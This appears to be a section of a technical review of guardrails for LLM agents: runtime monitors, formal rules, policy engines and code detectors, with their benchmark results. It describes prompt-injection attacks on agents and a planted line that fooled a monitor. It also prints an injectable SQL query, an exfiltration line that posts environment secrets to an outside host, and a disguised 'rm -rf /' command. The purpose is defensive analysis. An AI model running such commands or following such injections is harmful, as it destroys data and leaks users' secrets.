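Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), analysed what such a mechanism can achieve if it observes only the steps of a running program and stops the program just before a violation. One example policy forbids sending messages after reading a file. A monitor for this policy needs two states. It starts in "no file read", moves to "file read" when the program reads a file, and then rejects any attempt to send. Invariant's inbox rule has the same structure, with a suspicious inbox in place of the file.

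Schneider proved that these monitors can only enforce safety properties, which state that some bad thing never happens. For such a property, each run can be judged by itself, a run that violates the property stays in violation whatever comes next, and every violation shows up after a finite number of steps. A rule against sending after a file read meets all three conditions, because a run breaks the rule at its first send after a read and no later step can undo that.

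A requirement that something good must eventually happen is not a safety property. *What Can Be Enforced?* gives the example that every payment must eventually be followed by a confirmation. When the agent proposes the payment, no violation has occurred. If the guardrail allows the payment and the confirmation never comes, the money is gone. If it blocks the payment, it also interferes with runs in which the confirmation would have come. A guardrail that could hold the payment until the confirmation arrived would solve the problem, but it would have to withhold the call's result, which the agent may need for its next step. Changing the requirement so that the confirmation must come first is usually easier, and it makes the requirement a safety property.

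Restrictions on the flow of information fail for another reason. Suppose the summary of failed builds must not reveal anything about the passwords on the machine. Whether it does depends on what the agent would have written if the passwords had been different, and a monitor that watches one run cannot check that. The monitor can instead enforce a stricter policy, such as forbidding all messages once the agent has read a file containing passwords. This prevents the leak through messages but also blocks harmless ones. Some false positives therefore come from replacing the property the developer wants with one a monitor can check.

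Schneider's result also assumes that the monitor can stop every step. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (Basin, Jugé and colleagues) separates the actions a mechanism can prevent from those it can only observe. A guardrail can prevent a tool call, but it can't prevent a new email from arriving or an approval from expiring. If a rule requires the agent to finish a task within an hour, the guardrail can detect that the hour has passed but can't make the agent finish.

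Many useful rules fit within these limits. One policy in *What Can Be Enforced?* caps the total an agent may transfer to any recipient in a day. The monitor keeps a counter for each recipient and day. If the cap is $1,000 and the agent has already sent a supplier $800 that day, the monitor allows another $200 but blocks $300. Another policy forbids emailing personal data to recipients who are not on an approved list. The monitor can easily check the list, but it must rely on a fallible judge to decide whether a text contains personal data. The proof that the monitor enforces the policy therefore holds only if the judge is right, as with the classifier in Invariant's rule.

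A monitor also enforces the rules as written, and the rules together may permit something that nobody intended. *Tether* (2026), a policy engine for agents, checks for this before the agent runs. The developer describes a state that must never occur, and a language model tries either to prove that no sequence of permitted actions leads there or to find one that does. The proof assistant Lean checks the proof, so a mistake by the language model cannot produce a false guarantee about the policy as modelled. The policy in *Tether*'s experiments has 24 rules, plus many lists of permitted items and exceptions for file paths, so someone reading it could easily miss a gap.

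Most agent guardrails offer only limited guarantees. *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a 2026 survey, judges monitors such as AgentSpec the best compromise between practicality and demonstrated safety improvements, but notes that their guarantees cover only one or a few steps. A blocked agent may find another unsafe route that no rule covers.

### Formal rules tested on recorded attacks

The largest of the tests covered here used recordings. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, whose figures on the timing of alarms appeared earlier, wrote its rules in a temporal logic, a formal language for statements about the order and timing of events. Its five general rules all have the same form. An agent needs an earlier approval if it wants to delete something, switch off a protection, spend money, send data out, or change a device or its settings. For deletion, the rule is

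$$\text{always: } \forall a.\ \big(\text{destructive}(a) \rightarrow \text{once } \text{approved}(a)\big)$$

where "once" means at some earlier point in the run.

To apply the rules, the researchers sorted tools into classes by keywords in their names. In one recorded run, the agent searches a database, reads an entry, calls `confirm_for_deletion` and then calls `delete`. The translation drops the first two calls and records the other two as an approval and a destructive action. The rule does not flag the deletion because the approval came first. If the agent had skipped the confirmation, the rule would have flagged it. MonPoly, a general-purpose monitoring program, can check such formulas without custom code for each application.

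The AgentDojo recordings came from GPT-4o agents without other defences. The results differ a great deal between the benchmark's four settings.

| AgentDojo setting | Successful attacks flagged | Harmless runs flagged |
|---|---:|---:|
| Banking | 97.4% | 79.2% |
| Slack | 63.9% | 15.4% |
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 62.9% | 21.7% |
| Travel | 16.5% | 11.1% |
| All | 70.1% | 29.3% |

The rules flag nearly every banking attack because nearly all of these attacks move money, but most of the legitimate tasks move money too. AgentDojo gives each agent one user message at the start and no chance to ask for approval later, so the recordings contain no approvals. Any rule that forbids payments without approval therefore forbids all payments. The researchers point out that a list of forbidden keywords would have produced the same verdicts.

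The rule about sending data out flagged 27.9% of the successful attacks, the spending rule 26.8%, the rule about devices and settings 16.2%, and the deletion rule 15.9%. The deletion rule best separated attacks from harmless runs, since it flagged only 4.1% of the harmless ones. The rule about switching off protections never fired, because no tool in these settings does that.

STAC, the other main source of attacks, contains 483 chains of calls that look ordinary one by one but end in a harmful step. The rules flagged that final step in 71.8% of the chains. Three other monitors, one of them with a formally verified algorithm, flagged the same 347 chains as MonPoly, so a bug in the monitoring software probably doesn't explain the misses. In the 136 missed chains, the last action, such as a change to a calendar, fell outside the five classes. STAC has no harmless chains, so it can't be used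 to measure the rules' false-positive rate.

The rules did much worse on R-Judge, a collection of labelled agent records in which the harm often lies in the content of a message, such as bad advice or a breach of privacy. They flagged 23.6% of the unsafe records and 16.3% of the safe ones.

In this AgentDojo experiment, the rules raised alarms on 36 of 123 benign runs, or 29.3% (95% confidence interval 22.0% to 37.8%). *Stale Does Not Mean Unsafe* (Zheng, Long and colleagues, 2026) cites this figure as the share of benign runs on which formal monitors raise alarms. However, it describes five very general rules on recordings without approvals, and is not a typical error rate for formal monitoring. It is still far too high for these rules to block actions automatically. If one run in a thousand were a successful attack, only about one alarm in 400 would be correct.

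The attack benchmarks are unusual in lacking approvals. The researchers also examined 1,980 runs from τ-bench, in which agents handle airline and retail customers and must get confirmation before changing anything. In 52.5% of those runs, the user gave explicit permission before the change. The general rules could separate approved from unapproved actions there, but τ-bench contains no attacks to test them on.

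### More precise rules and the records they depend on

The researchers got better results with a rule that uses more of the history. In the banking setting, it fires only if the agent sends money to an account that has not already appeared as a sender or recipient in the account data. Compared with the general rule about spending money, it reduced false alarms from 44% to 24% of harmless runs, but it also reduced detection of successful attacks from 79.2% to 70.0%. The false-alarm rates come from only 25 harmless runs. Across 700 harmless banking runs pooled from many models, though, the new rule removed 75 false alarms and added none, so the reduction in false alarms is probably real.

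The more precise rule also gave attackers a new way to evade the monitor. The monitor recognised a known account by its format in the text of the trajectory, for example after the word "recipient". When the researchers planted a single line in that format with the attacker's account number, the monitor missed 94% of the attacks that the rule had flagged. The line only had to fool the monitor, not the agent. The researchers then changed the rule to treat an account as known only if it appeared in the answer to a lookup that the agent had actually made. After this change, none of the planted lines worked, and the detection and false-alarm rates on the original recordings stayed the same. An attacker who controls the tool that answers the lookup could still defeat the rule.

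Zheng and colleagues found the same two effects in database operations. In their tests, an agent reads a record and proposes a change, but another process alters the record before the change takes effect. One guard blocked the agent's action whenever the record's version number had changed. Another checked only the facts that made the action safe, such as whether a data snapshot had passed validation. Neither guard allowed an unsafe write under the conditions the researchers had declared. But across 1,600 harmless alterations, the version guard blocked 80% of the agent's actions, while the more specific guard blocked none.

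The specific guard failed on all five additional hazards that its conditions did not mention. The version guard allowed unsafe writes in 4.9% of decisions when it used the version number that the model had written into its proposal instead of the one that the software had recorded. A precise rule therefore needs the right conditions and a record that neither the agent nor an attacker can alter. Tests on clean recordings may not reveal that a rule uses the wrong record.

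### Identical calls with different purposes

*Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* describes two banking runs in which the agent reads the inbox, looks up past transactions and sends money. In the harmless run, the money goes to a supplier whose account number is in the transaction history. In the attack, it goes to an account that appears only in a planted email. The rule about known accounts can distinguish the legitimate account from the other, which is impossible for a rule that checks only the last call.

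Now suppose the planted email asks the agent to pay the real supplier a second time. The tools, the amount and the known account number can all match a run where the user asked for the second payment. A deterministic rule that reads only the calls and the account data has to give both runs the same verdict. It misses the attack if it allows both payments, and raises a false alarm if it blocks them. A daily cap would limit the damage but still treat the two payments alike.

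Sending the build summary to an outside contractor's channel is likewise part of the job if the user asked for it, but a leak if the agent is following an instruction in a build log. A detector therefore has to take the user's request into account. AgentSpec passes that request to its predicates, but a developer would still have to write a function that decides whether the request covers the call. Because people phrase requests in so many ways, that function would in practice need to use a language model.

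## How the rules are written and how tight they are

A language model can read the user's request before the agent acts and write rules that ordinary software then enforces. Developers can also write the rules by hand, as in the AgentSpec tests, or have a model translate them from policy documents. All three methods turn ordinary language into conditions that a program can check, and a mistake in that step carries over into every later verdict.

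### One sentence, two rules

Chen, Kang and Li (2025), in *SHIELDAGENT*, describe a guardrail that translates policy documents into logical rules. Their prompt gives the translating model the example "only authorized users can access personal data" and tells it to write this as

$$(\text{authorised} \land \text{legitimate need}) \rightarrow \text{access}$$

An appendix to the same paper writes a similar restriction, on deleting data, the other way round. Applied to access, that version is

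$$\neg\,\text{authorised} \rightarrow \neg\,\text{access}$$

| Situation | First rule | Second rule |
|---|---|---|
| Authorised user with a need; agent reads the data | satisfied | satisfied |
| Authorised user with a need; agent does something else | violated | satisfied |
| Unauthorised user; agent reads the data | satisfied | violated |

The first rule can never block an access, because an if-then statement is true whenever its second half is true. It would raise an alarm when an authorised user's agent did something other than read the data. The second rule matches the sentence. ShieldAgent later corrects bad translations, so its finished rules may not contain this error.

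The second rule still depends on what "authorised" means. In the paper's examples, the word could mean that the user has permission to act on the data, or that the user has consented to the agent's action. If an employee without access rights tells an agent to delete a confidential file, the rule blocks the deletion under the first reading and allows it under the second.

### ShieldAgent: from a handbook to weighted rules

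ShieldAgent uses GPT-4o to split documents, such as the staff handbook of the software company GitLab, into policies. The model records each policy's definitions, scope, exact text and source, then translates it into temporal logic, using predicates for the action ("delete data") and the situation ("the data is confidential"). One GitLab policy forbids accessing, modifying, deleting or disseminating confidential information without authorisation, but the rule printed beside it covers only deletion, so an agent could still publish the data unless other rules forbid it.

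GPT-4o next rewrites or splits vague rules and merges duplicates. It repeats both steps until nothing changes or the budget runs out. To find vague rules, ShieldAgent compares the embeddings of the rules' predicates, since a predicate that closely resembles many others is probably too general. Experts may review the result. ShieldAgent then groups the rules by action, so that a proposed deletion triggers only the rules relevant to deletion.

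When the agent proposes an action, ShieldAgent retrieves the relevant rules and works out whether each condition is true. It can search the run's history, ask a small model a yes-or-no question, or call a content-moderation service. It then runs code to check each rule.

A violation doesn't automatically block the action. Some extracted rules will be inaccurate, and treating them all as absolute could cause many false alarms. Each rule *r* therefore has a weight *θ<sub>r</sub>*, learned from actions labelled safe or unsafe. ShieldAgent compares two outcomes *w*, one in which the action happens and one in which it doesn't:

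$$P(w) = \frac{1}{Z}\exp\!\Big(\sum_{r\ \text{satisfied in}\ w}\theta_r\Big), \qquad \text{allow if } P(\text{act}) - P(\text{not act}) \ge \varepsilon$$

*Z* scales the probabilities, and the developer chooses *ε*. In an invented example, an agent tries to delete an expired confidential file without authorisation. A confidentiality rule with weight 2 forbids this, but a retention rule with weight 1 requires expired files to be deleted. The probabilities are 0.27 for deleting and 0.73 for not deleting, so with *ε* = 0 ShieldAgent blocks the deletion. If training had given the confidentiality rule a weight of only 0.5, the probabilities would be 0.62 and 0.38, and ShieldAgent would allow the deletion even though it violates the confidentiality rule.

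On recorded runs of web agents, ShieldAgent was 91% accurate on average and wrongly flagged 4.8% of safe runs. GPT-4o, checking the same policies one rule at a time, was 82% accurate and wrongly flagged about 17%. But the attacks targeted policies that the extraction had already found, so the results don't show how often extraction misses a policy in a document. When ShieldAgent checked a web agent's actions live, the share of successful GitLab tasks that complied with policy rose from 22.8% to 50.7%.

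### GuardAgent and Conseca: rules for one check or one task

Xiang, Zheng and colleagues (2024), in *GuardAgent*, have a language model write a program for each check. The developer supplies rules in ordinary language, for example which hospital databases each role may open, and describes the format of the agent's logs. The model first writes a plan with four steps:

1. Identify the key terms in the rules, such as the roles.
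2. Select the permissions that apply to this user.
3. Find the databases that the agent used in its log.
4. Compare the permitted databases with the ones used.

The model then writes a Python program from the plan, using similar past cases and a set of ready-made functions, and GuardAgent runs it. If the program fails to run, the model can try up to three times to fix it.

In one case, a nurse's question required the medication and diagnosis databases, but nurses had no access to the diagnosis database. An LLM judge with the same rules wrongly added that database to the nurse's permissions and allowed the query. GuardAgent's program compared the required databases with the permitted ones and denied it. Across 316 hospital cases, GuardAgent with GPT-4 was right 98.7% of the time, only slightly better than the judge's 97.5%. It was much better at explaining denials, identifying every forbidden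 item in 97.5% of the cases that it should have denied, compared with 67.9% for the judge.

On 200 web tasks with rules about age, membership and similar conditions, GuardAgent missed 20% of violations and the judge missed 35%. Neither raised false alarms. GuardAgent did worst on a rule about films, music and videos, because the model failed to recognise that some requests fell under it. Running code makes the comparison reliable, but the model still has to decide which rule applies.

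Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025), in *Contextual Agent Security*, argue that fixed rules cannot cover all the tasks of a general-purpose agent. For example, whether an agent should delete an email depends on what the email contains, whether the user wants to erase sensitive messages or clear out junk, and whether the account is for work or private use. When a task arrives, their system, Conseca, has a model write a policy based on the request and trusted context, in a form that a person can check. Ordinary software then tests each proposed action against the policy. For the build summary, the model could write the same two rules as in the Progent example. An instruction hidden in a build log could not change them, because the model writes them without seeing the log.

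*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* argues that Conseca is secure only if the model that writes its policy is safe. Like other checks on single actions, Conseca can also miss harm that an agent under an attacker's influence spreads over several steps. Human review might catch a bad policy, but users are unlikely to read a new one carefully for every task.

### LeanGuard: trusted facts and a proved check

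In *LeanGuard*, Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026) write policies in Lean, a proof assistant and programming language. In their example, an agent is handling an exchange for an online shop. An attacker injects text into a tool's output to tell the agent that the customer has already agreed to pay the price difference with a certain gift card, which belongs to the attacker.

LeanGuard takes its facts from a snapshot of the shop's database and its own journal of earlier events, and doesn't accept text in tool outputs as evidence. A record of the customer's consent counts only if it matches the exact call, its arguments and the current state of the database, and each consent covers one call. LeanGuard blocks the exchange because the customer has not confirmed it and the gift card is not on the account. It also records every permitted call before the tool runs, so if the connection drops during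 a refund, the agent can't simply issue the refund again.

The policy consists of Lean functions that return true or false, for example on whether an order belongs to the customer. Others can look back in the journal, for example to check that the agent has already read this order. Lean compiles the functions into a program that applies the following test:

$$\text{allow} \iff \text{some permit holds} \land \text{every requirement holds} \land \text{no prohibition holds} \land \text{no error occurs}$$

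Missing or malformed data counts as an error, so it blocks the call. Otherwise a missing record might satisfy a condition such as "the order has not been cancelled".

Sankar and colleagues also defined the meaning of the policy language separately, in temporal logic. They proved that the compiled program agrees with this definition for every possible history, so any call LeanGuard allows satisfies the formal policy. Lean checks the proof when the developer builds the policy, so the monitor doesn't have to prove anything during a run. The guarantee holds only if the database snapshot is accurate and every consequential call goes through LeanGuard.

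The proof doesn't show that the policy matches what people meant. If a developer entered the first version of the personal-data rule above as a requirement, the proof would still hold, but the requirement would never block an access. For the customer-service tests, an LLM-based tool drafted the rules from written policies and the researchers corrected them by hand, producing 45 rules for 43 tools in 583 lines of Lean. Two rules were stricter than the written policies, and 164 of the blocked calls violated only those two.

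An LLM judge also compared the agents' conversations with the written policies. It flagged 88 conversations in which LeanGuard had approved every executed call. Some of these flags were the judge's mistakes, but others involved requirements missing from the Lean policy, such as a limit on the total extra mobile data a customer could buy. In a few conversations, the consent record was wrong, for example because it left out the customer's payment limit.

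### What LeanGuard blocks and repairs

Sankar and colleagues tested five Qwen models, with 0.8 to 27 billion parameters. They used τ²-bench, the successor to the customer-service benchmark τ-bench, and DTap, which tests both direct prompt injection and indirect injection, hidden in content the agent reads. In the results below, LeanGuard's feedback to the agent identified the violated rule and included a hint.

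| Measure | Without LeanGuard | With LeanGuard |
|---|---:|---:|
| τ²-bench: tasks completed | 72.7% | 70.9% |
| τ²-bench: conversations flagged by the judge | 9.7% | 6.5% |
| DTap: direct attacks that succeeded | 57.9% | 5.9% |
| DTap: indirect attacks that succeeded | 22.3% | 3.8% |
| DTap: harmless tasks completed | 53.1% | 12.5% |

Without LeanGuard, the agents on τ²-bench executed at least 33 forbidden calls, in 28 of 1,390 conversations. With it they executed none, as expected from a monitor that blocks whatever the policy forbids. The agents completed fewer tasks with LeanGuard. The overall drop could be due to chance, but in the retail setting the drop was 7.9 percentage points.

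The DTap attack figures look better than they are because the agents had permission only to read data, so LeanGuard also blocked legitimate bookings and trades. Of the 1,918 harmless cases that agents solved only without LeanGuard, 992 first failed when it blocked patient registration. The telecoms results are more encouraging. Harmless tasks there rarely require changing data, so completion stayed at about 75% while the success rate of direct attacks fell from 55.1% to 2.4%. Across DTap, the attacks that still succeeded caused harm through the agent's text, such as a misreported bill, which LeanGuard does not check.

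LeanGuard can also search for a corrected version of a denied call. It tries up to 32 changes and returns the first new call that Lean can prove the policy allows. A separate condition specifies which changes preserve the user's intent. If an account has spent 60 of a budget of 100 and the agent tries to spend 70, the repair could reduce the 70 to 40, as long as the task allows a smaller amount.

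The researchers replayed 1,613 denials from τ²-bench, 252 of which were due to the values of the call's arguments. The search repaired 88 of these, taking a median of 2 milliseconds per denial. In 64 cases it changed the call to send a refund to the original payment method, and in 18 it changed the call to charge a flight change to a card instead of a travel certificate. A customer might well object to the second kind of repair, and the proof shows only that the policy permits it. The agents never received the repairs, so the test doesn't show whether the repairs would help agents complete more tasks.

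### Ajar: measuring what a guardrail leaves open

A guardrail can stop every attack in a benchmark while allowing many other actions that the task doesn't need. *Ajar* (Sharma, Lin and colleagues, 2026) measures these unnecessary permissions using AgentDojo's harmless tasks. In one of them, the user asks the agent to read a landlord's notice and adjust the rent. The agent has to read the file, list the scheduled payments and change payment 7 to 1,200. *Ajar* replays these correct steps without running an agent, and at each step it also tests whether the guardrail would allow other calls, such as reading another file or redirecting payment 6 to an attacker. The result therefore doesn't depend on which calls an agent proposes.

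Ajar built 10,471 tests from 97 tasks. Its main measure is leakage, the share of unnecessary calls that the guardrail allows, weighted by harm:

$$\text{leakage} = \frac{\text{total weight of unnecessary calls allowed}}{\text{total weight of unnecessary calls tested}}$$

The weights run from 1 for a reversible read to 27 for an irreversible action that affects money or other people. In a test set with one call of each kind, allowing only the read would give a leakage of 4%, and allowing only the irreversible action would give 96%. Blocking everything would give zero leakage, so Ajar also measures how many necessary calls the guardrail allows.

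Sharma and colleagues compared Progent and Claude Code's auto mode with three other systems. Permission Assistant uses a model to predict whether the user would permit a call, CaMeL tracks where the data in a call came from, and AC4A has a model write an access policy once per task. In the results below, Claude Sonnet 5 wrote the policies or judged the calls.

| Guardrail | Leakage | Necessary calls allowed | Tasks completed without → with guardrail |
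|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Permission Assistant | 8.1% | 96.1% | 85.6% → 74.2% |
| CaMeL | 9.0% | 70.0% | 86.6% → 64.9% |
| Progent | 10.3% | 90.2% | 87.6% → 87.6% |
| AC4A | 11.1% | 71.5% | 85.6% → 50.5% |
| Claude Code auto mode | 30.1% | not measured | 92.4% → 89.0% |

For comparison, a list of exactly the tools that each task needs had a leakage of 35.5% when it didn't limit their arguments, and 0.2% when it also fixed the arguments from the known solutions. In the rent task, Progent and AC4A would have let the agent set the payment to 0.01, while CaMeL refused even the correct amount. Permission Assistant allowed the correct amount but not 0.01.

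Progent and AC4A had similar leakage, but the agents' task completion rate was 37 percentage points higher with Progent. Part of Progent's advantage may come from updating its policy during the run. Without updates, its leakage was 16.1% and it allowed about the same share of necessary calls.

Auto mode is designed to stop actions that are destructive, irreversible or aimed outside the user's environment, so it can be expected to allow many unnecessary reads. Those reads explain only part of its leakage, because the weighting already counts them for little. It also allowed the calls needed for 74 of 581 AgentDojo attacks, compared with 16 to 46 of 609 for the other four systems.

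The differences in leakage among those four are too small to rank them. AC4A's leakage ranged from 9.6% to 13.6% over three runs with identical inputs. AgentDojo's checks also confirm only 27% of Ajar's labels. The rest depend on Ajar's rules for what a task needs, which count a call as unnecessary if it reaches the goal with a tool the reference solution doesn't use. The researchers also couldn't test whether lower leakage prevents more attacks, because their agent ignored AgentDojo's standard injection even without a guardrail.

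## Code detectors: reading the program before it runs

Rules about tool calls help little when an argument is a whole script. A code detector analyses the script as a program, usually by static analysis, which examines code without running it.

### Insecure code and harmful code

Developers use static analysis to find out whether code will be insecure later, and also whether running it now does harm. These are different questions. In an example from Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues (2025), in *LlamaFirewall*, a coding agent has to let a website filter its users by email domain, and it copies a database query of this form from the web:

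```python
"SELECT * FROM users WHERE email LIKE '" + domain + "'"
```

Running this on the developer's machine does no damage, but once the website is live, a visitor could enter database commands instead of a domain, and the database would execute them. The build-summary script, by contrast, contains no weakness for a later attacker to exploit, but running it once sends the machine's passwords to an outside address.

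A developer can have the agent correct insecure code at any time before release, but a guardrail has to stop harmful code before it runs. Judging whether code is harmful also depends more on the circumstances than judging whether it is insecure. *Purple Llama CyberSecEval* (Bhatt, Chennabasappa and colleagues, 2023) gives the example of a script that encrypts a home directory, which could protect the owner's privacy or be part of a ransom attack.

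Agents often fail to write secure code. The survey *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026) describes a benchmark of 105 C and C++ tasks based on real vulnerabilities. The best combination of agent and model produced a correct and secure solution 23.8% of the time. This figure doesn't establish the survey's conclusion that agents are more often wrong about security than right, because solutions that were secure but didn't work also counted as failures.

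### Text patterns, syntax trees and data flow

The simplest code detector searches the program's text. Suppose it flags any line that contains both `requests.post` and `os.environ`. This rule catches the last line of the build-summary script, but it also flags a harmless comment that quotes that line, and it misses the call if the agent splits it over two lines.

A syntax-tree rule avoids both errors. A parser first converts the program into a tree of calls, arguments and assignments, and the rule then looks for a call to `requests.post` with `os.environ` somewhere in its arguments. Line breaks make no difference to the tree, and comments are not part of it. But the rule misses this version:

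```python
settings = dict(os.environ)
report = {"metrics": settings}
requests.post(METRICS_HOST, json=report)
```

Data-flow analysis can catch it. The developer lists sources, where secrets enter the program, and sinks, where data leaves it. The analysis marks data from a source as tainted and follows it through the program. For an assignment *x* = *e*, the basic rule is

$$x \text{ is tainted} \iff e \text{ reads a source or uses a tainted variable}$$

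Here `settings` is tainted because its value comes from `os.environ`, and `report` is tainted because it contains `settings`. The third line passes `report` to a sink, so the detector raises an alarm. It does not raise one for the request that posts the build summary, because the build server is not on the list of sources.

| What the script does | Text pattern | Syntax-tree rule | Data-flow analysis |
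|---|---|---|---|
| Posts `os.environ` directly, as in the original | alarm | alarm | alarm |
| Makes the same call over two lines | no alarm | alarm | alarm |
| Copies `os.environ` into a variable first | no alarm | no alarm | alarm |
| Quotes the call in a comment | alarm | no alarm | no alarm |
| Posts a password from `os.environ` to log in to the build server | alarm | alarm | alarm |
| Downloads another script and runs it | no alarm | no alarm | no alarm |

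The login is harmless, but more precise analysis would not remove the false alarm, because the script does send the password to the network. The developer could allow passwords to be sent only to the build server, but the detector would then need to determine each request's destination, which this script gives only by name.

Existing tools differ in how deeply they analyse code. *Agent Audit* (2026) describes Bandit as matching patterns in Python syntax trees, Semgrep as matching patterns in more than 30 languages, and CodeQL as tracing tainted data across function calls. CodeQL's approach would be needed if the script passed `settings` to a helper function that made the request.

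*SkillsMetric* (Chen, Ji et al., 2026) measures how well static analysis detects different attacks in skills, the packages of instructions and scripts that developers add to an agent. The detector combines five scores, including one for suspicious text and one for data flow. The data-flow score has the largest weight because a complete path from a secret to the network is rare in harmless code. The researchers inserted attacks into real skills and wrote others from scratch. The detector caught 93% of the skills that stole data but only 28% of those that fetched a remote script. It caught none of the 11 that destroyed files, because they used the same library calls as ordinary clean-up scripts and sent nothing over the network.

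The percentages are rough because these groups contain at most 29 skills each and the attacks are synthetic, but the differences are too large to be due to chance. Chen and colleagues also scored the instruction files of 138,133 public skills. Most of the highest-scoring skills they inspected were legitimate security tools, such as virus scanners, which have good reasons to contain dangerous-looking code.

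### CodeShield

CodeShield, the code scanner in Meta's LlamaFirewall, uses Semgrep rules and regular expressions (text patterns) to find more than 50 types of security weakness in code. It scans in two tiers. The first takes about 60 milliseconds and passes code with a possible problem to the second, a fuller analysis that takes about 300 milliseconds. In Meta's own deployment, about 90% of inputs needed only the first tier. Insecure code that the first tier misses never reaches the second.

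For the database query above, CodeShield would reject the agent's change, and the agent could try again until it wrote a query that keeps the visitor's text separate from the database command.

Chennabasappa and colleagues report that CodeShield had a precision of 96% and a recall of 79% on hand-labelled completions, so it missed about one in five of the insecure ones. They attribute the test to a 2024 benchmark, but Bhatt and colleagues had already published the same figures in December 2023 for a detector with 189 rules, tested on 50 completions per programming language. The figures therefore probably describe old rules applied to the output of old models.

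Bhatt and colleagues' test probably also overstates recall, because they used the detector itself to find insecure lines in open-source code. They then asked models to continue the code that came before those lines or to write similar code, so the completions were likely to contain the kinds of weakness that the detector's rules already covered.

The detector's precision depends on how much of the code is insecure. Across the whole benchmark, the detector found insecure code in about 30% of completions. If the share in the hand-labelled sample was similar, a precision of 96% implies a false-positive rate of about 1.4%. In a project where 5% of the code was insecure, only about three-quarters of alarms would be right at the same error rates.

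None of this measures how well CodeShield detects scripts like the build summary. Chennabasappa and colleagues list malicious code execution among the risks LlamaFirewall should cover in future.

### Shell commands in disguise

Agents also run short shell commands, and these are easy to disguise. The command `r=rm; $r -rf /` deletes everything the user has permission to delete, but it doesn't contain the text `rm -rf`. In the first version of AgentTrust, from May 2026, Yang tries to undo such disguises before checking the command against its rules. The system replaces variables and aliases with their values, decodes characters written as numeric codes, joins words that quotation marks have split, and fills in the output of simple `echo` and `printf` commands. The first of its nine rewrites turns the example into `rm -rf /`.

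AgentTrust checks the original command and every rewritten version, then uses the most severe verdict. A rewrite can therefore add an alarm but can't remove one. None of the nine rewrites merges separate options, so a rule against `rm -rf` must also cover `rm -r -f` explicitly.

On Yang's set of 630 actions, about 95 of which contained disguised commands, the rules missed 15.7% of dangerous actions without the rewrites and 6.4% with them. Both figures are lower than they would be on new commands, because Yang had added rules after seeing which of these actions the system missed. The comparison is still useful because the rules were the same in both cases.

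The system rewrites text and never executes any part of a command. Yang rejected a full shell parser for this version, partly because it would tempt developers to run embedded commands to see their output, and so execute the attack they were checking for. As a result, deeply nested disguises can get through. In one test, a deletion hidden in numeric codes inside an `eval` command received only a warning.

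### Which threats rules can decide

In the June 2026 successor to AgentTrust, Yang argues that rules cannot determine whether an action is a threat when that depends on intent. His clearest example is `kubectl get secret`, which reads a stored credential. An engineer may run it to debug a failing service, and a thief may run the same command. In another example, an agent uploads either a finished build or stolen secrets to the same approved storage service.

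Yang wrote his additional cloud rules to test whether a lack of rules was the only problem. He tried them on 189 new actions that a second person had labelled without seeing the original labels, and had five language models judge the same actions.

| Detector | Exact verdict correct | Harmless actions flagged | Dangerous actions missed |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Original rules | 48.1% | 22.4% | 52.9% |
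| With the additional cloud rules | 56.1% | 22.4% | 33.3% |
| DeepSeek | 69.8% | 31.0% | 5.7% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 75.7% | 0.0% | 11.5% |
| GPT-5.5 | 83.6% | 6.9% | 1.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 84.1% | 0.0% | 2.3% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 85.2% | 1.7% | 4.6% |

Yang's results table labels five categories as dependent on intent. He emphasises that the new rules brought no improvement in three of them, but accuracy in the other two rose by 12 and 13 percentage points. The new rules also reduced misses by almost 20 points without flagging any more harmless actions. This is hard to reconcile with his claim that each such rule only trades a missed attack for a false alarm. The eight categories average about 24 actions each, so one action changes a category's accuracy by about four points.

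The argument is strongest for `kubectl get secret`, but there it applies equally to language models. An LLM judge can distinguish the two cases only if it also receives the user's request or the history of the run, as with the second payment to a real supplier. Yang's other pairs often differ in ways that a better rule could detect. For example, he contrasts a database query that returns 100 rows with one that sends a whole table to an outside program, and a detector that parses the query can distinguish them.

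### What static analysis cannot settle

Even a perfect data-flow analyser would face a mathematical limit. Suppose a detector could always decide correctly whether a program will ever send the environment variables to `METRICS_HOST`. Take any program *P* that sends nothing itself, and give the detector this script:

```python
run(P)
requests.post(METRICS_HOST, json=dict(os.environ))
```

The script sends the variables only if *P* finishes, so a correct verdict from the detector would reveal whether *P* finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that this question is undecidable, meaning that no general method can answer it for every program. A static detector that always gives a verdict must therefore make mistakes. Its designer has to choose between flagging some harmless programs in order to miss no harmful ones and missing some harmful programs in order to avoid false alarms.

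Most scripts that agents write are short, so a more common obstacle is that some of the code is missing when the detector checks the script. A script can download text from a web address and execute it, as in the last row of the earlier table, and the detector has only the address. If the detector downloads the text to check it, the server can return something harmless and then send the real attack to the agent. Installing a software package is a similar problem because the package may run code that doesn't appear in the install command.

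Running the program in a sandbox, an isolated environment, can reveal what it downloads. *The Devil Wears Markdown* (2026) describes a system that records system calls, network traffic and file changes while an agent carries out a skill's instructions in a sandbox. The system doesn't accept the agent's own statements as proof of what happened. According to the paper, one run without harmful behaviour is not enough to call a skill benign, because the agent chooses which permitted actions to try and may never reach the harmful step.

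### Running only code that passes a conservative check

A guardrail can instead reject every program that the analysis can't show to be safe, and confine whatever the analysis doesn't cover. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes a system called TACIT that does this. The agent writes its actions in a restricted form of the programming language Scala 3, and TACIT runs the code only if it passes the compiler's checks.

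In this language, a program needs a value called a capability to use a file, a network connection or another resource. The type of each function lists the capabilities it might use. TACIT keeps secret data in a container, and the agent can apply a function to the contents only if that function has no capabilities. In simplified notation:

```scala
secrets.map(text => text.length)
secrets.map(text => network.post(text))
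```

The compiler accepts the first line, but the result stays in the container. It rejects the second line because the function uses the network. If the agent prints a secret, the user can read it but the agent receives only a placeholder.

The list of capabilities includes everything the function might use, even in a branch that never runs, so the compiler rejects some harmless programs. It would also reject a program that ran *P* and then posted the secrets, without having to determine whether *P* ever finishes, which is undecidable.

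Odersky and colleagues tested two models on 131 trials each. The trials combined ordinary tasks with prompt injections, and included 11 direct or disguised requests for secrets. Neither model leaked any secrets when they were kept in containers. Without containers, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in 2 trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11. The researchers designed this test around the property the compiler enforces, so the perfect score is less surprising than it looks. They also ran TACIT on AgentDojo, where it blocked all but one of the injections.

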